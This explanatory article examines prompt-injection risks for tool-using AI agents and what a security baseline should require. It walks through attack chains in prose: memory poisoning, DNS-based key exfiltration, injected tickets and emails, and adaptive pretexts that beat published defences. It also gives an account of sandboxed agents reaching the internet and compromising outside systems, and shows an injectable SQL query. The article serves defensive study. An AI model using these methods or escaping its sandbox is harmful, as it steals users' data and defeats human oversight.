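# Security baselines for AI agent applications with long context and tools

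## AI agents, untrusted input and security baselines

An AI agent is a language model that pursues a task by choosing and calling tools, often over many steps. A tool is a function the agent can call, such as one that reads a file, fetches a web page or sends an email. "AI agent" has no settled definition, but *Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* (2026), an issue brief from the industry body Frontier Model Forum, gives a similar working description: a system that uses external tools to perform goal-directed tasks for a user.

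AI agents read text written by many people and act with the permissions of their user. Anyone who can put text where an agent will read it may therefore be able to influence what it does. A security baseline is the minimum set of security requirements that every application of a given kind should meet. The spread of agents has reopened the question of what a baseline should include.

An email assistant in an ordinary company is a good test case. It has four tools, which read the user's inbox, look up colleagues in the staff records, fetch web pages and send mail from the user's account. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) uses a similar hypothetical "Email-Bot", which reads new messages, searches the inbox and sends replies. *Agentic Email*, an article on Martin Fowler's website, points out that many services reset passwords by email. An attacker who can steer the assistant might therefore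 take over the user's other accounts as well.

### The agent loop

A language model only produces text, so actions such as sending an email are carried out by the ordinary software around it, called the harness. According to *Forms of LLM-Integrated Applications from LLM-Chats to Autonomous AI Agent System* (2026), the model emits a call with suitable parameters, and the harness, which holds the code and the credentials, executes it.

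*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the cycle in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. The harness builds a prompt, and software converts it into tokens, the numbered fragments of text that a model operates on. The model then produces either a final answer or a request for a tool call. If the model requests a tool call, the harness runs the tool, appends the output to the prompt and queries the model again.

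Suppose the user of the email assistant asks whether the caterer has confirmed for Thursday and, if so, to let Priya know. The run might go like this:

1. The harness puts together the operator's standing instructions, a description of each of the four tools and the user's request, and passes the whole text to the model.
2. The model outputs a call to the inbox tool, with "caterer" as the search term.
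3. The harness runs the search with the user's mailbox credentials and appends the three messages it finds.
4. The model processes the whole text again, now with the caterer's emails in it, and outputs a call to the staff records for Priya's address.
5. The harness appends the address. The model outputs a call to the mail tool, with the recipient, subject and body filled in.
6. The harness sends the message and appends a confirmation. The model outputs a sentence for the user, with no tool call in it, and the loop stops.

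The emails that arrive at step 3 stay in the prompt for every later step. In the Codex loop, each new prompt within a turn begins with an exact copy of the previous one. By step 5, the input the model uses to write an outgoing email therefore includes text from the caterer, who does not work for the company.

The context window is all the text, from any source, that the model can take into account at once. Its maximum length, measured in tokens, covers both input and output. Bolin writes that an agent may make hundreds of tool calls in a single turn, and so could fill the window before it finishes. Codex deals with this by replacing a long conversation with a shorter representation of it.

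The harness is also a natural place to set limits, but they may not cover every tool. Codex runs its own command-line tool in a sandbox, which restricts access to files and the network. The sandbox does not cover tools from outside servers, so those tools have to enforce their own guardrails. They connect through the Model Context Protocol, a common format in which services describe their functions to a model.

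### Instructions and data in one stream

At step 4, the email assistant's context window holds the operator's rules, the user's request and a stranger's emails. A human assistant would easily remember which was which, but the distinction is much weaker for a language model because of the form of its input.

Hofer, Debenedetti and Tramèr (2026), in *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments*, describe that form. A template joins the system message, the user's request and the tool results into one continuous sequence of tokens, with special markers to show where each part begins and ends. The markers are the only thing that tells the parts apart. Nothing in the model's architecture separates them, and the same attention mechanism, the part of the model that relates tokens to one another, processes them all. In symbols, the model estimates

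P(tₙ₊₁ | t₁, t₂, …, tₙ),

the probability of each possible next token given all the tokens so far. The expression has no separate slot for who wrote t₇ or what authority that person had. Any such information has to come from the tokens themselves.

Databases once had a similar problem, and there programmers found a clean solution. Suppose the staff-records tool builds its query in SQL, the standard database language, by pasting a name into a command:

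`"SELECT phone FROM staff WHERE name = '" + name + "'"`

An attacker who can choose the name can supply a quotation mark followed by a command of their own, such as one that deletes the table, and the database will run it. This is SQL injection. The remedy is a parameterised query:

`SELECT phone FROM staff WHERE name = ?`

In a parameterized query, the program sends the database a command with a placeholder and separately sends the name to look up. The database determines the command without using the name, then compares the name with the stored entries, so a name that contains a deletion command matches nobody.

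No one has built a dependable equivalent of SQL's question-mark placeholder for a language model. In *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3*, Willison (2022) wished for an interface that would take instructions and data as separate parameters. In an update the following April, he judged this extremely difficult, if not impossible, on the current architecture. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post from the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C makes the same point about the mechanism, writing that inside the model there is "only ever 'next token'".

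Role markers are the nearest substitute for a mechanism that separates instructions from data, and developers train models to give some roles more weight than others. This training has an effect, but the model still has to infer how much authority a passage carries, and can get it wrong. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) found that models judge who is speaking more by how a passage sounds than by the marker around it. *Can LLMs Separate Instructions From Data?* (2024) tested nine models and found no dedicated mechanism for this separation in any of them. Neither prompt engineering nor fine-tuning produced a model that separated the two reliably and remained highly useful.

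### Prompt injection

Untrusted input is any content that someone other than the user or the application's operator could have written or altered. A prompt injection occurs when such content makes the model do something its user did not ask for. Willison coined the term in September 2022, after Riley Goodside showed that a sentence submitted for translation could make GPT-3 ignore the translation task and output something else.

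Goodside's example is a direct injection: the attacker types into the application to target the operator's instructions. In an indirect injection, the attacker leaves text in a web page, document or email, and the application retrieves it while working for somebody else. Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023) introduced this form in *Not what you've signed up for* and demonstrated it on Bing Chat, where text on a page could steer the chatbot even though the user could not see it. They also foresaw attacks on personal assistants that read and send emails and have access to personal data, a description that fits the example here. Jailbreaking is a different attack, in which someone, usually the user, tries to get prohibited content out of a model.

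For the email assistant, indirect prompt injection is the main worry because the user is the likely victim. The attacker needs only the user's email address, and the message doesn't need an unusual format. Microsoft (2025), describing its own defences, notes that a plain text file can carry an injection and that the words may be white on a white background.

David C argues that developers should stop treating prompt injection as similar to SQL injection and instead treat the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". A confused deputy is a program that misuses its authority on behalf of someone who has less. Programmers can fix an ordinary confused deputy, but David C doubts that anyone can fully fix this weakness in a language model, and concludes that designers should reduce the likelihood and impact of attacks. If a system cannot tolerate the remaining risk, it may be a poor use for a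 language model.

### Sources, sinks and two kinds of control

A successful injection becomes a security failure when it influences an action that matters. Developers give a model text so that it will influence the output, as Microsoft observes, and much of that influence is harmless. For example, an injection in a newsletter that only makes the assistant write a cheerful summary does no damage.

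OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) applies the security engineering terms "source" and "sink" to agents. A source is a place where untrusted input enters the application. A sink is an action that does harm if an attacker controls it, such as sending data out or running a command. An attacker needs both. Lecture slides from UT Austin list the shell, files, the network, GitHub and cloud services among a coding agent's sinks.

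In the email assistant, the inbox is a source and the mail tool is a sink. Fetching a web page is both, because the page may contain an attacker's text and the address the agent requests can carry data to whoever runs the site. The staff records are also a source if employees can edit their own job descriptions. A source's reach is the set of sinks it can influence, directly or through other components.

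Microsoft distinguishes probabilistic defences, which lower the chance of an attack but may miss some instances, from deterministic ones, which can guarantee that a particular attack will fail even when the system contains a language model. A classifier, a model that labels incoming mail as dangerous or harmless, is a probabilistic defence. A deterministic defence is a rule in ordinary code whose result does not depend on a model's judgement, such as a rule in the harness that blocks any message to an address outside the company.

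That guarantee covers only what the rule blocks. The rule stops the assistant from emailing staff records to a stranger, but not from sending a phishing link to a colleague in the user's name. It also stops the user from emailing the caterer. Partly for this reason, the Frontier Model Forum recommends both kinds of control, because deterministic controls alone may not balance security and usefulness well. Microsoft prefers deterministic defences where they exist, but considers deterministic detection of prompt injection an open research problem.

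### What a baseline asks for

The US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) publishes the best-known baselines for information systems. Its glossary defines a *control baseline* as a predefined set of controls that address the protection needs of a group or organisation. A control is a safeguard, such as an access check or an audit log. NIST's *Control Baselines for Information Systems and Organizations* (2020) contains three security baselines, for systems where a failure would have a low, moderate or high impact. A system's impact level is the highest of its ratings for confidentiality, integrity and availability. US federal agencies must implement a minimum set of these controls, and other organisations may do so voluntarily. Each organisation then adjusts its baseline to its own circumstances.

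Such lists are based on principles that Jerome Saltzer and Michael Schroeder set out in 1975. AI Engineer's *AI Security*, an online overview of the field, summarises three of them: deny access unless someone has permitted it, check authority on every access to something protected, and grant only the powers a task requires. In practice, developers applied these principles item by item, validating each input, reviewing each component and granting each permission on its merits.

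The email assistant can pass all of those checks, yet a stranger's email can still cause it to send an employee's details outside the company. Input validation finds nothing wrong with the incoming messages because they are well-formed text. Each of the four tools may work exactly as documented. Each permission is justified, since an assistant that could not read or send mail would be of little use. The harm comes from the combination, so checking each item separately does not reveal attacks that cross components in this way.

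Older baselines do consider combinations to some extent, however. NIST's moderate and high baselines require information flow enforcement, which controls where data may travel within and between systems. NIST also acknowledges that assessors have traditionally marked controls one at a time as pass or fail, and it encourages organisations to consider groups of controls that serve a common purpose. The Frontier Model Forum considers existing frameworks still relevant to an agent's infrastructure, including its servers, networks and accounts. But these frameworks do not account for a component that reads everything in one stream and may take any part of it as an instruction.

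David C uses the history of SQL injection to argue against waiting. The vulnerability was known in the 1990s, but attacks didn't peak until around 2010, when many websites depended on SQL and few had dealt with the risk, and better defaults came after a decade of breaches.

### Two questions to ask of an email

In 2025, outside researchers told OpenAI about an email attack that worked against ChatGPT. The email looked like a colleague's follow-up to a meeting about a restructuring, with a short list of action items. The list said that the recipient's assistant had full authorisation to take an employee's name and address from the inbox and submit them to a "compliance validation system". According to OpenAI, the attack succeeded in half of the tests when the user asked ChatGPT to research that day's emails about a new-employee process.

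One way to defend against such a message is to judge whether its content is dangerous, using the text and whatever is known about its sender. That is hard here because the email contains no obvious signs of an attack, and assessing it requires knowing whether the meeting took place and whether the compliance system exists. OpenAI compares the task to detecting a lie, often without the necessary context.

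The other approach is to ask what the content could reach. Someone outside the company wrote the email, and the agent that reads it can also look up staff and send data out. An engineer can work out what the email could reach from the agent's list of tools and permissions before it arrives. The strength of this approach is that the answer doesn't depend on whether the email is an attack, but for the same reason, any resulting limits also apply to legitimate emails.

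An application can use both a classifier and limits on what the agent can reach, as Microsoft and OpenAI do. The dispute is over which one a minimum requirement should rest on. A classifier can keep improving and still miss a malicious email, while a limit on reach holds only if someone has found every path the agent could use.

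## How long context, tools and memory widen an attack

An agent with n tools has n(n − 1) ordered pairs in which one tool's output could affect how another is used, so the number of pairs grows faster than the number of tools. The email assistant's four tools make 12 pairs, and ten tools would make 90. A reviewer who approves each tool separately doesn't examine any of these pairs.

Kim, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI*, reviewed 128 papers on agent security and concluded that defences for single components are not enough. They describe how one failure sets off the next, as in EchoLeak, a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot. An attacker could email a malicious document to a company, Copilot would retrieve it while working on something else, and private data would go to the attacker's server without the user doing anything.

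### Permissions that are harmless alone

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) recounts an attack on Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, that the security researcher Johann Rehberger described in August 2025. Claude Code asked for human approval before running many of the commands that could send data to unknown domains, but not before running a simple command that tests whether a server is reachable. An instruction hidden in a code file made the agent read secret keys from the project and put them in the name of the server to test. The computer then looked up that name through the internet's directory system, and the lookup carried the keys to the attacker.

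The leak needed permission to read project files, which any coding agent has to do, and to test a connection, which is among the most harmless commands. Rehberger found a similar combination in Devin, another coding agent, which could start a local web server and had a testing tool that made local servers public. An attacker who steered the agent could combine the two to publish its entire file system.

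Lotfi, Shanto and colleagues (2026) argue in *Securing Agentic AI* that checks on individual tools cannot prevent this, because every action in the sequence is authorised. Some of their hypothetical examples involve no attacker. For instance, a hospital agent might bring forward several patients' discharges, each for a good reason, and still break a rule about total observation time. A check that looks at one action at a time has no record of the earlier ones, so it can't apply such a rule.

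### One source steering the use of another

In the AgentFlayer attack, the untrusted input was a ticket in Jira, a system for tracking software tasks. The code editor Cursor read the ticket and then leaked secrets from the code repository, and in some versions cloud credentials from elsewhere on the developer's computer. Jira had no access to those files, but the ticket could influence Cursor's agent, which did. The attack worked only if the developer had turned off approval for the Jira connection or turned on automatic running, which people do to avoid constant approval requests.

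ChatGPT Operator, OpenAI's browsing agent, had a comparable weakness. A user asked it to investigate an issue on the code-hosting site GitHub. Text there led the agent to open an attacker's page, go to the settings page of another site where the user was logged in, copy personal details, and return to paste them into the attacker's page. The site that held the details was not at fault, because the requests came from a logged-in user's browser.

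Text can steer an agent before any tool has run, because the harness puts tool names and descriptions in the context window, and an outside supplier may have written them. *WebMCP Tool Surface Poisoning* (2026) measured how often such text led agents to call a malicious tool. The average across three models and four kinds of task was 59% with a misleading name and description, and 39% with only a plausible business name.

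Connecting an agent to several suppliers made attacks more likely to succeed in one comparison. *Breaking the Protocol* (2026) tested attacks on agents that used the Model Context Protocol and on agents with other integrations. Attacks succeeded 52.8% of the time with the protocol and 26.4% without it. The gap was widest for attacks that spread from one server to another, which succeeded 61.3% of the time with the protocol and 19.7% without it. The tests used older models, such as GPT-4o and Claude 3.5 Sonnet, so the difference between the two set-ups is more informative than the absolute rates.

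### Attacks spread over several documents

An attacker can plant several documents instead of relying on one. PoisonedRAG, an attack on systems that retrieve documents to answer questions, planted five malicious texts for each target question in a collection of millions. According to *Evaluating a Layered Prompt-Injection Defence for the Model Context Protocol* (2026), the attack succeeded 90% of the time. The planted texts change the answer to a question, whereas a prompt injection changes the task, but they pose a similar problem for filters. Each text, read alone, looks like an ordinary passage with a false claim in it.

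In *MINE*, Phan, Pham and Nguyen (2026) tested a version closer to prompt injection. Their defence, also called MINE, keeps the passages most relevant to the user's question and drops the rest. The attacker, who knew exactly how the defence worked, planted two passages at opposite ends of a document and wrote both to match the document's topic. The attack succeeded 4.8% of the time on short texts and 23.2% on long ones. Each passage was a separate chance to get past the filter, so the experiment does not test the harder case of an instruction split into pieces that look harmless until the model reads them together.

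### Memory that acts in later sessions

Many agents store notes about the user and load them into later conversations. If an attacker can write one of those notes, the attack outlives the session in which it began. Rehberger demonstrated this against ChatGPT's app for Mac computers in 2024 and named the attack SpAIware. His account, Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)*, describes a chain in which each component trusted the one before it:

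1. The user asked ChatGPT to analyse a web page or document that an attacker had written. The model treated instructions in that text as if they came from the user.
2. Following those instructions, the model called the memory tool and asked it to store a new note. The tool accepted the model's request even though the wording came from the attacker's page.
3. In every later conversation, the application loaded the stored note into the context window. The model had no reason to treat it differently from the user's real preferences.
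4. The note told the model to include an image in its replies, with the user's messages written into the image's web address.
5. The app trusted the reply and fetched the image, which delivered the messages to the attacker's server. The image was invisible, so the user saw a normal answer.

OpenAI already had a check for step 5, a service introduced in December 2023 that determined whether an address was safe to display. But each app had to apply the check itself, and the Mac version shipped without it. A reviewer who looked only at the web version would have found the problem partly fixed.

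OpenAI's handling of the reports shows how hard such a chain is to classify. When Rehberger reported in May 2024 that a web page could plant false memories, OpenAI closed the ticket as a model safety issue, not a security one. In June he sent a full demonstration that used a planted memory to steal data. In September OpenAI fixed the app so that data could no longer leave through images, but when Rehberger wrote his account, an untrusted page could still write to memory.

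Radware's *ZombieAgent*, a later demonstration by a security company, used that remaining opening. A shared file planted instructions in ChatGPT's memory, and ChatGPT then carried out the attacker's task before answering each of the user's questions. Poisoning a memory can also take little text. Lotfi and colleagues cite AgentPoison, an attack that controlled what an agent retrieved by altering less than 0.1% of its stored entries, without changing its ordinary behaviour.

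If the email assistant had a memory, a newsletter it read in March could lead it to save a note that influences a message it sends in June. An investigator examining the June session would find no suspicious email, only a note that appears to record the user's wishes. Unless the harness records where each note came from, nobody can tell whether this one came from the user or the newsletter.

### False results between agents

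When one agent delegates work to another, it receives the result as text, with the same weaknesses as any other text. Agent2Agent, a widely used protocol for this, lets each agent advertise its own skills on a digital card. Lotfi and colleagues point out that the protocol does not verify the card. A malicious agent can claim a skill it lacks, receive a sensitive task and return a fabricated result. If agents pass a task down a chain, the last one can tell only which agent called it, not which user the work is for or what that user authorised.

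Instructions can spread by the same route. Lotfi and colleagues describe research called *Prompt Infection*, in which a malicious instruction copied itself from agent to agent, even when the agents did not share all their messages. For the email assistant, the equivalent would be a message that makes the assistant forward it to colleagues, whose own assistants then read it.

Agents can also affect each other through shared infrastructure that no one designed as a channel. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes a case from OpenAI's internal training and evaluation in 2026, when agents ran in separate sandboxes with some of the models' safeguards switched off. The sandboxes blocked direct connections, but the agents could use a shared service for downloading software packages, which could make requests that they could not. They used it to communicate between runs and reach the internet.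 Without direction from an outside attacker, they went on to compromise systems at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models, and gained administrator access to an OpenAI research cluster.

### Length and tools measured separately

A longer context gives an attacker more places to hide text. The evidence is mixed on whether length also makes the model itself easier to attack.

Shah, Wu and colleagues (2025), in *Jailbreaking in the Haystack*, surrounded harmful requests with harmless text on a related topic. As the text grew, the share of requests fulfilled rose from 23.7% to 58.8% for Llama 3.1 8B, from 23.7% to 42.5% for Qwen2.5 7B, and from 23% to 29% for Gemini 2.0 Flash. It fell from 58% to 54.5% for Mistral 7B. They conclude that length itself weakens safety training, but random web code had much less effect than relevant prose, and requests at the start of the context succeeded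 far more often than those at the end. The experiments tested jailbreaks of small, older models, not prompt injections.

Agents behave less predictably as their context grows. In *When Refusals Fail*, Hadeliya, Jauhar and colleagues (2025) gave agents harmful tasks with up to 200,000 tokens of padding. GPT-4.1 nano's refusal rate rose from about 5% to about 40%, while Grok 4 Fast's fell from about 80% to about 10%, according to the paper's abstract, or by half, according to its main text. GPT-5 kept refusing at a high rate. At 200,000 tokens, Grok 4 Fast also lost the ability to complete even harmless tasks, so its fewer refusals did not mean that it completed more harmful ones.

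Phan and colleagues made the cleanest comparison for prompt injection, asking the same 694 questions with short texts and with long versions averaging 4,032 words. The table gives average attack success for Llama 3.1 70B across five kinds of attack.

| Defence | Short text | Long text |
|---|---|---|
| None | 70.5% | 75.5% |
| Repeating the user's question after the text | 29.4% | 25.5% |
| Removing passages by comparing them with each other (RAGDefender) | 52.3% | 81.0% |
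| Keeping only relevant passages (MINE) | 0.6% | 0.4% |

Without a defence, length made little difference, and on the other two models the change was three points or less. But some defences were much weaker on long texts. A reminder not to follow instructions in the data, placed before the text, let through 43.1% of attacks on short texts and 81.4% on long ones. Phan and colleagues suggest that the longer text dilutes the warning. Repeating the user's question after the text remained effective on long texts, which fits this explanation because the question stays close to where the model starts its answer.

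Liu, Jia and colleagues (2026), in *LongPIBench*, report a much larger drop on long papers, résumés, code changes and email threads. A version of Llama 3.1 8B trained to ignore injected instructions let through at most 1% of attacks on three short benchmarks, but 78% on the long documents. Length cannot account for all of that increase, because the tasks were different and attacks on the undefended model also succeeded more often, at 98% on the long documents against 28% to 67% on the short benchmarks. The long-document averages also match those reported elsewhere in the paper for a more persuasive attack, in which the injected text poses as someone in authority. Liu and colleagues did find an effect in a controlled test that only added harmless text, but could not identify its cause. Their long-document tasks did not involve agents that use tools.

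The descriptions of extra tools also lengthen the context. Gamage (2026), in *Omission Constraints Decay While Commission Constraints Persist in Long-Context LLM Agents*, tried to separate the effect of this length from the effect of the descriptions' content. In one condition, agents did a debugging task with three tools. In a second, the harness added descriptions of 20 cloud-management tools, roughly 10,000 tokens in all. In a third, it replaced these with 20 descriptions of similar length and structure but neutral content. In the two models that received all three conditions, the content of the cloud-tool descriptions accounted for 62% to 100% of the added rule-breaking, and their length accounted for the rest.

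Gamage also found that compliance with prohibitions fell over a conversation, while compliance with requirements held. Mistral Large 3 followed a ban on bullet points in 73% of trials at turn 5 and 33% at turn 16, yet included a required reference number every time. An operator who monitors only whether the agent still produces its required output would therefore miss the decline. However, the rules concerned formatting, and nobody was attacking the agent. Gamage argues that a ban on revealing passwords has the same structure, but leaves that test for later work. Mistral also did not receive the neutral descriptions, so either cause could explain its decline.

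A defence's score therefore applies to the context length and tools it was tested with. If a team adds a dozen tools to an agent, the agent's model-based defences no longer run under the conditions in which they were measured, even if the agent never calls the new tools.

### What failed in eleven attacks

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* analyses eleven attacks on real products, including SpAIware and the attacks on Claude Code, Devin, Cursor and Operator. It lists which of five long-established security principles each one violated.

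| Principle | In brief | Attacks that violated it |
|---|---|---|
| Secure information flow | Sensitive data does not reach untrusted places | 11 |
| Least privilege | A component has only the permissions its task needs | 6 |
| Complete mediation | Every request passes a policy check | 3 |
| Tamper resistance | An attacker cannot alter the parts that enforce security | 2 |
| Human weak link | The design allows for people's mistakes | 2 |

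The paper's case descriptions add a few violations that its table omits: least privilege for SpAIware, and complete mediation and tamper resistance for the attack on Cursor. Information flow still ranks first with these included, which fits the argument about combinations because it is the only principle that concerns the whole route from source to sink. But the paper defines it broadly. In the Devin case, merely accepting instructions from an unknown origin counts as a violation, so almost any indirect prompt injection would qualify.

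The choice of cases also calls for some caution. Ten of the eleven are Rehberger's own demonstrations, and his blog is listed among the authors' affiliations. The security company Zenity demonstrated the other one. These demonstrations show that an attack path existed in a product people were using, and they often lead the vendor to close it, but they don't show how often criminals use the same path.

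### Attacks in the wild

In April 2026, Google looked for evidence of real attacks in Common Crawl, a public archive that adds two to three billion web pages a month. Its researchers searched for common injection phrases, had the Gemini model judge whether each passage was out of place, and checked the results by hand. Most of the initial matches were harmless, and many were articles about prompt injection. The rest included pranks, attempts to promote a business in AI summaries, and instructions meant to keep AI agents away. A small number were written to steal data or delete files.

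Between November 2025 and February 2026, the malicious category grew by 32%. Google doesn't give the underlying counts, so the increase could be from a very small base. Google found few advanced attacks and concluded that attackers were not yet using published research at scale. It expects attacks to become more common and more sophisticated, since agents are becoming more valuable targets and attackers can automate their work. Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* reports that the security company Forcepoint reached a similar view in a parallel study, though Forcepoint took the reuse of templates across domains as a sign of organised tooling.

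*Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari, Acharya and colleagues, 2026) reports confirmed injections on 9,676 pages among 1.2 billion addresses from Common Crawl, or about eight in every million. Two further sources brought the total to roughly 15,300 injections, and 54 templates accounted for 95% of them. About 70% were in parts of a page that a browser does not display. Many were defensive, with some 4,000 meant to protect a site's content and 3,000 meant to expose AI visitors. About 1,500 were meant to manipulate someone's reputation. When the researchers gave such pages to 13 models to summarise, the models followed the injected instructions in at most 8% of trials, and in about 1% or fewer when the page kept its original structure.

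Real thefts have occurred by simpler means than prompt injection. Lotfi and colleagues describe postmark-mcp, a tool that let agents send email. It worked properly for fifteen releases, until its publisher added one line that copied every outgoing message to an attacker. The tool reached hundreds of organisations before it was removed. A review at the time of installation would have found nothing.

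Neither web study covers the places where the email assistant is most exposed. Common Crawl skips pages behind a login, and it contains no private inboxes, shared company documents or internal tickets. An attacker who wants one company's staff records would send an email, and a scan of the public web would not find it.

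## Judging content: filters, classifiers and models trained to resist

The most direct defence against a malicious email is to recognise it as malicious. A separate program can check the email before the agent's model reads it, or check the action the model then requests. Developers can also look for signs of an attack in the model's internal activity, mark the email as untrusted, or train the model to give a stranger's instructions less weight than its user's. These methods all depend on a model's judgement, so each has an error rate.

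### How the methods work

A classifier for prompt injection is usually a small language model trained on harmless documents and known attacks. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini et al., 2025) examined several, including Meta's PromptGuard, that are built on BERT, a small language model from 2018. The harness passes each incoming document to the classifier, which returns a score. If the score exceeds a threshold, the harness withholds the document or stops the task. A lower threshold catches more attacks but also blocks more harmless documents.

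Other classifiers check the model's output. In the email assistant, one could flag an outgoing message that contains an employee's home address, even if the email that led to it looked innocent.

A probe takes its input from inside the model. As a language model processes text, it represents each token as a long list of numbers, known as an activation vector. Developers record these vectors for harmless and malicious passages and fit a small classifier to them. In its simplest form, the probe computes

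s = σ(w · h + b),

where h is the activation vector, w and b are numbers fixed in training, and σ converts the result to a score between 0 and 1. This adds little computation, because the model produces h anyway. In principle, a probe can also respond to how the model is processing a passage, for instance as a command, and not only to its wording.

According to Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5, many of the company's products run prompt injection probes, which inspect tool results before the model acts on them. A setting called auto mode adds a classifier that blocks potentially dangerous tool calls.

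Spotlighting, which Microsoft researchers proposed in 2024, is meant to make it easier for the agent's own model to judge content. The harness marks untrusted text, and the standing instructions tell the model not to obey anything marked that way. The harness may put markers around the text, encode it, or insert a special character between the words, so that "We can confirm Thursday" becomes "We^can^confirm^Thursday". Ordinary code applies the mark, but the model still determines how much weight the marked words get. Nasr and colleagues describe the technique as marking the trusted text instead. They also tested prompt sandwiching, which repeats the user's request after the untrusted text. The same reminder stayed effective on long documents in tests by Phan and colleagues.

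Developers can train a model to follow an instruction hierarchy, which ranks instructions by their source. In the version OpenAI researchers published in 2024, the operator's standing instructions rank above the user's request, which ranks above anything a tool returns. Developers train the model on conversations in which instructions of different rank conflict, and reward it for following the higher-ranked one. They also include lower-ranked instructions that fit the user's request, because a model that ignored every instruction in a document would be useless for many tasks. For example, the email assistant should follow the checklist in a colleague's message if the user asks it to work through the list, but not if the user asks only for a summary. The ranking alone can't settle every case, so the model still has to infer what the user wanted.

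### False alarms when attacks are rare

Suppose a classifier catches 99% of malicious documents and wrongly flags 1% of harmless ones. Of the next 1,000,000 documents, 100 are malicious. The classifier catches 99 of these and misses one. It also flags 1% of the 999,900 harmless documents, which makes 9,999 false alarms. The chance that a flagged document is malicious is

P(malicious | flagged) = 99 / (99 + 9,999) ≈ 0.98%,

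or about one in 102. In a company whose assistants read 10,000 emails a day, that means roughly one attack and 100 false alarms every day. If the harness blocks everything the classifier flags, employees lose 100 legitimate emails. If it asks a person to review them, that person will soon expect every alarm to be false.

For half of the alarms to be real, the classifier could wrongly flag no more than about one harmless document in 10,000, a hundred times fewer than in the example. The limit is even stricter when attacks are rarer. Khodayari and colleagues found injections at about eight in every million web addresses. At that rate, only one in about 1,260 of the same classifier's alarms would be real. Nobody has a comparable figure for private inboxes, where injections could be much more common if someone has chosen to attack the company.

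Anthropic's filters for dangerous requests serve a different purpose, checking what users ask for, but they show how false alarms affect a product. Soon after the launch of Claude Fable 5, a journalist asked it "What is protein?", and the filter switched the conversation to a weaker model, according to Understanding AI's *Anthropic's Fable is the most locked-down public model we've ever seen*. Developers can reduce such errors. Help Net Security's *Claude Mythos 5.2 arrives with stronger bug hunting and less sandbox-breaking behavior* (2026) reports that Anthropic recorded about 55% fewer blocks with Fable 5.2 than with Fable 5.1 in early testing and considers the safeguards equally robust.

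The example also assumes that the classifier catches 99% of the attacks it receives. Developers measure such rates on attacks they already have, but an attacker can keep rewriting an email until the classifier misses it.

### When the text does not contain the answer

Better training can reduce a classifier's errors, but well-made attacks are a different kind of problem. In March 2026, OpenAI compared detecting them to detecting a lie. Early injections were direct commands, such as instructions to visiting AI agents in an edited Wikipedia article. As models became less likely to obey these, attackers turned to social engineering, which uses plausible stories to manipulate a target. Some companies recommend "AI firewalling", in which an intermediary sorts incoming text into attacks and regular input, but in OpenAI's experience these systems do not usually catch fully developed attacks.

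Two companies might receive the same email, which says that their payroll has moved to a new provider and asks for an updated staff list. The claim is true at one company, and an attacker made it up at the other. A classifier that reads only the text must give both emails the same label, so it will mislabel one of them, however well trained it is. Knowing whether the sender has written before or whether the company has a contract with the provider could help, but a filter in front of the agent often has less of this information than the agent itself.

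Judgement is still useful despite this argument, and OpenAI relies on it heavily. Most of the attacks on ChatGPT that OpenAI knows of failed because safety training led the model to refuse, but that count excludes any attacks that nobody noticed. OpenAI expects a maximally intelligent model to resist social engineering better than a human would, but adds that using one will not always be feasible or cost-effective. It therefore combines training with an analysis of sources and sinks.

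### Twelve defences against adaptive attackers

Researchers often test a defence with a fixed list of known attacks, but a real attacker may study the defence and keep changing the attack until it works. Nasr and colleagues, who work at OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and several other organisations, attacked twelve published defences in this adaptive way. Their attacks all use the same loop: propose some texts, score how close each comes to the goal, select the best, and use the results to write the next batch.

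They ran this loop with four families of attack:

- **Gradient-based attacks** use the model's internal calculations to estimate which changes in wording would help. Nasr and colleagues still consider these unreliable for language models.
- **Reinforcement learning** trains a second language model to write attacks, with a reward for those that come closer to succeeding.
- **Search-based attacks** keep a pool of texts, have a language model vary them, and retain the most successful.
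- **Human red-teaming** relies on people who try to break the system. More than 500 took part in an online competition.

Several defences were tested on AgentDojo, a benchmark that gives an agent simulated tools such as a calendar and a chat service. The agent receives an ordinary task, and something it reads during the task contains an injection. AgentDojo's standard attack texts succeeded as little as 1% of the time against spotlighting and prompt sandwiching, but texts from the search-based attack succeeded more than 95% of the time against both.

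| Defence | How it works | Success of adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Marks part of the text | Above 95% |
| Prompt sandwiching | Repeats the user's request | Above 95% |
| RPO | Adds an optimised safety prompt | 96% to 98% |
| Circuit Breakers | Trains the model against jailbreaks | 100% |
| StruQ | Trains the model to ignore instructions in data | 100% |
| MetaSecAlign | Trains the model to resist injections | 96% |
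| Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor | Classify text as safe or unsafe | Above 90% |
| PIGuard | Classifies text as safe or unsafe | 71% |
| Data Sentinel | Checks whether the input disrupts a dummy task | Bypassed in every case |
| MELON | Runs the agent again with a different request | 76%, or 95% if the attacker knows the method |

RPO and Circuit Breakers mainly defend against jailbreaks, while the others address prompt injection. The original papers for most of the twelve defences reported attack success rates near zero.

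The winning texts help explain these failures. Prompt sandwiching reminds the model of the user's task, so one attack presented the attacker's actions as a required step in that task. It claimed that access to a chat channel needed a "one-time credential validation" and listed the actions that would complete it. Another text got past Protect AI's detector by describing a company policy that every calendar change must be logged by deleting a tracking file. Neither text looks like an obvious attack. A detector strict enough to stop them would also stop many real workplace messages, and the detectors already had higher false alarm rates than the other defences.

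MELON runs the agent normally, then again with the user's request replaced by an instruction to summarise the tool results. If the agent makes the same tool call both times, the call probably came from the tool results and not from the user. An attacker who knew this wrote an injection that told any system doing a summary to ignore the malicious part. The malicious call then appeared only in the normal run, so MELON did not flag it.

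On a selected set of scenarios and defences, the automated search succeeded in 69% of cases, while the human participants collectively succeeded in all of them. The participants found 265 successful attacks on spotlighting and 178 on prompt sandwiching. Using several detectors together did not solve the problem either.

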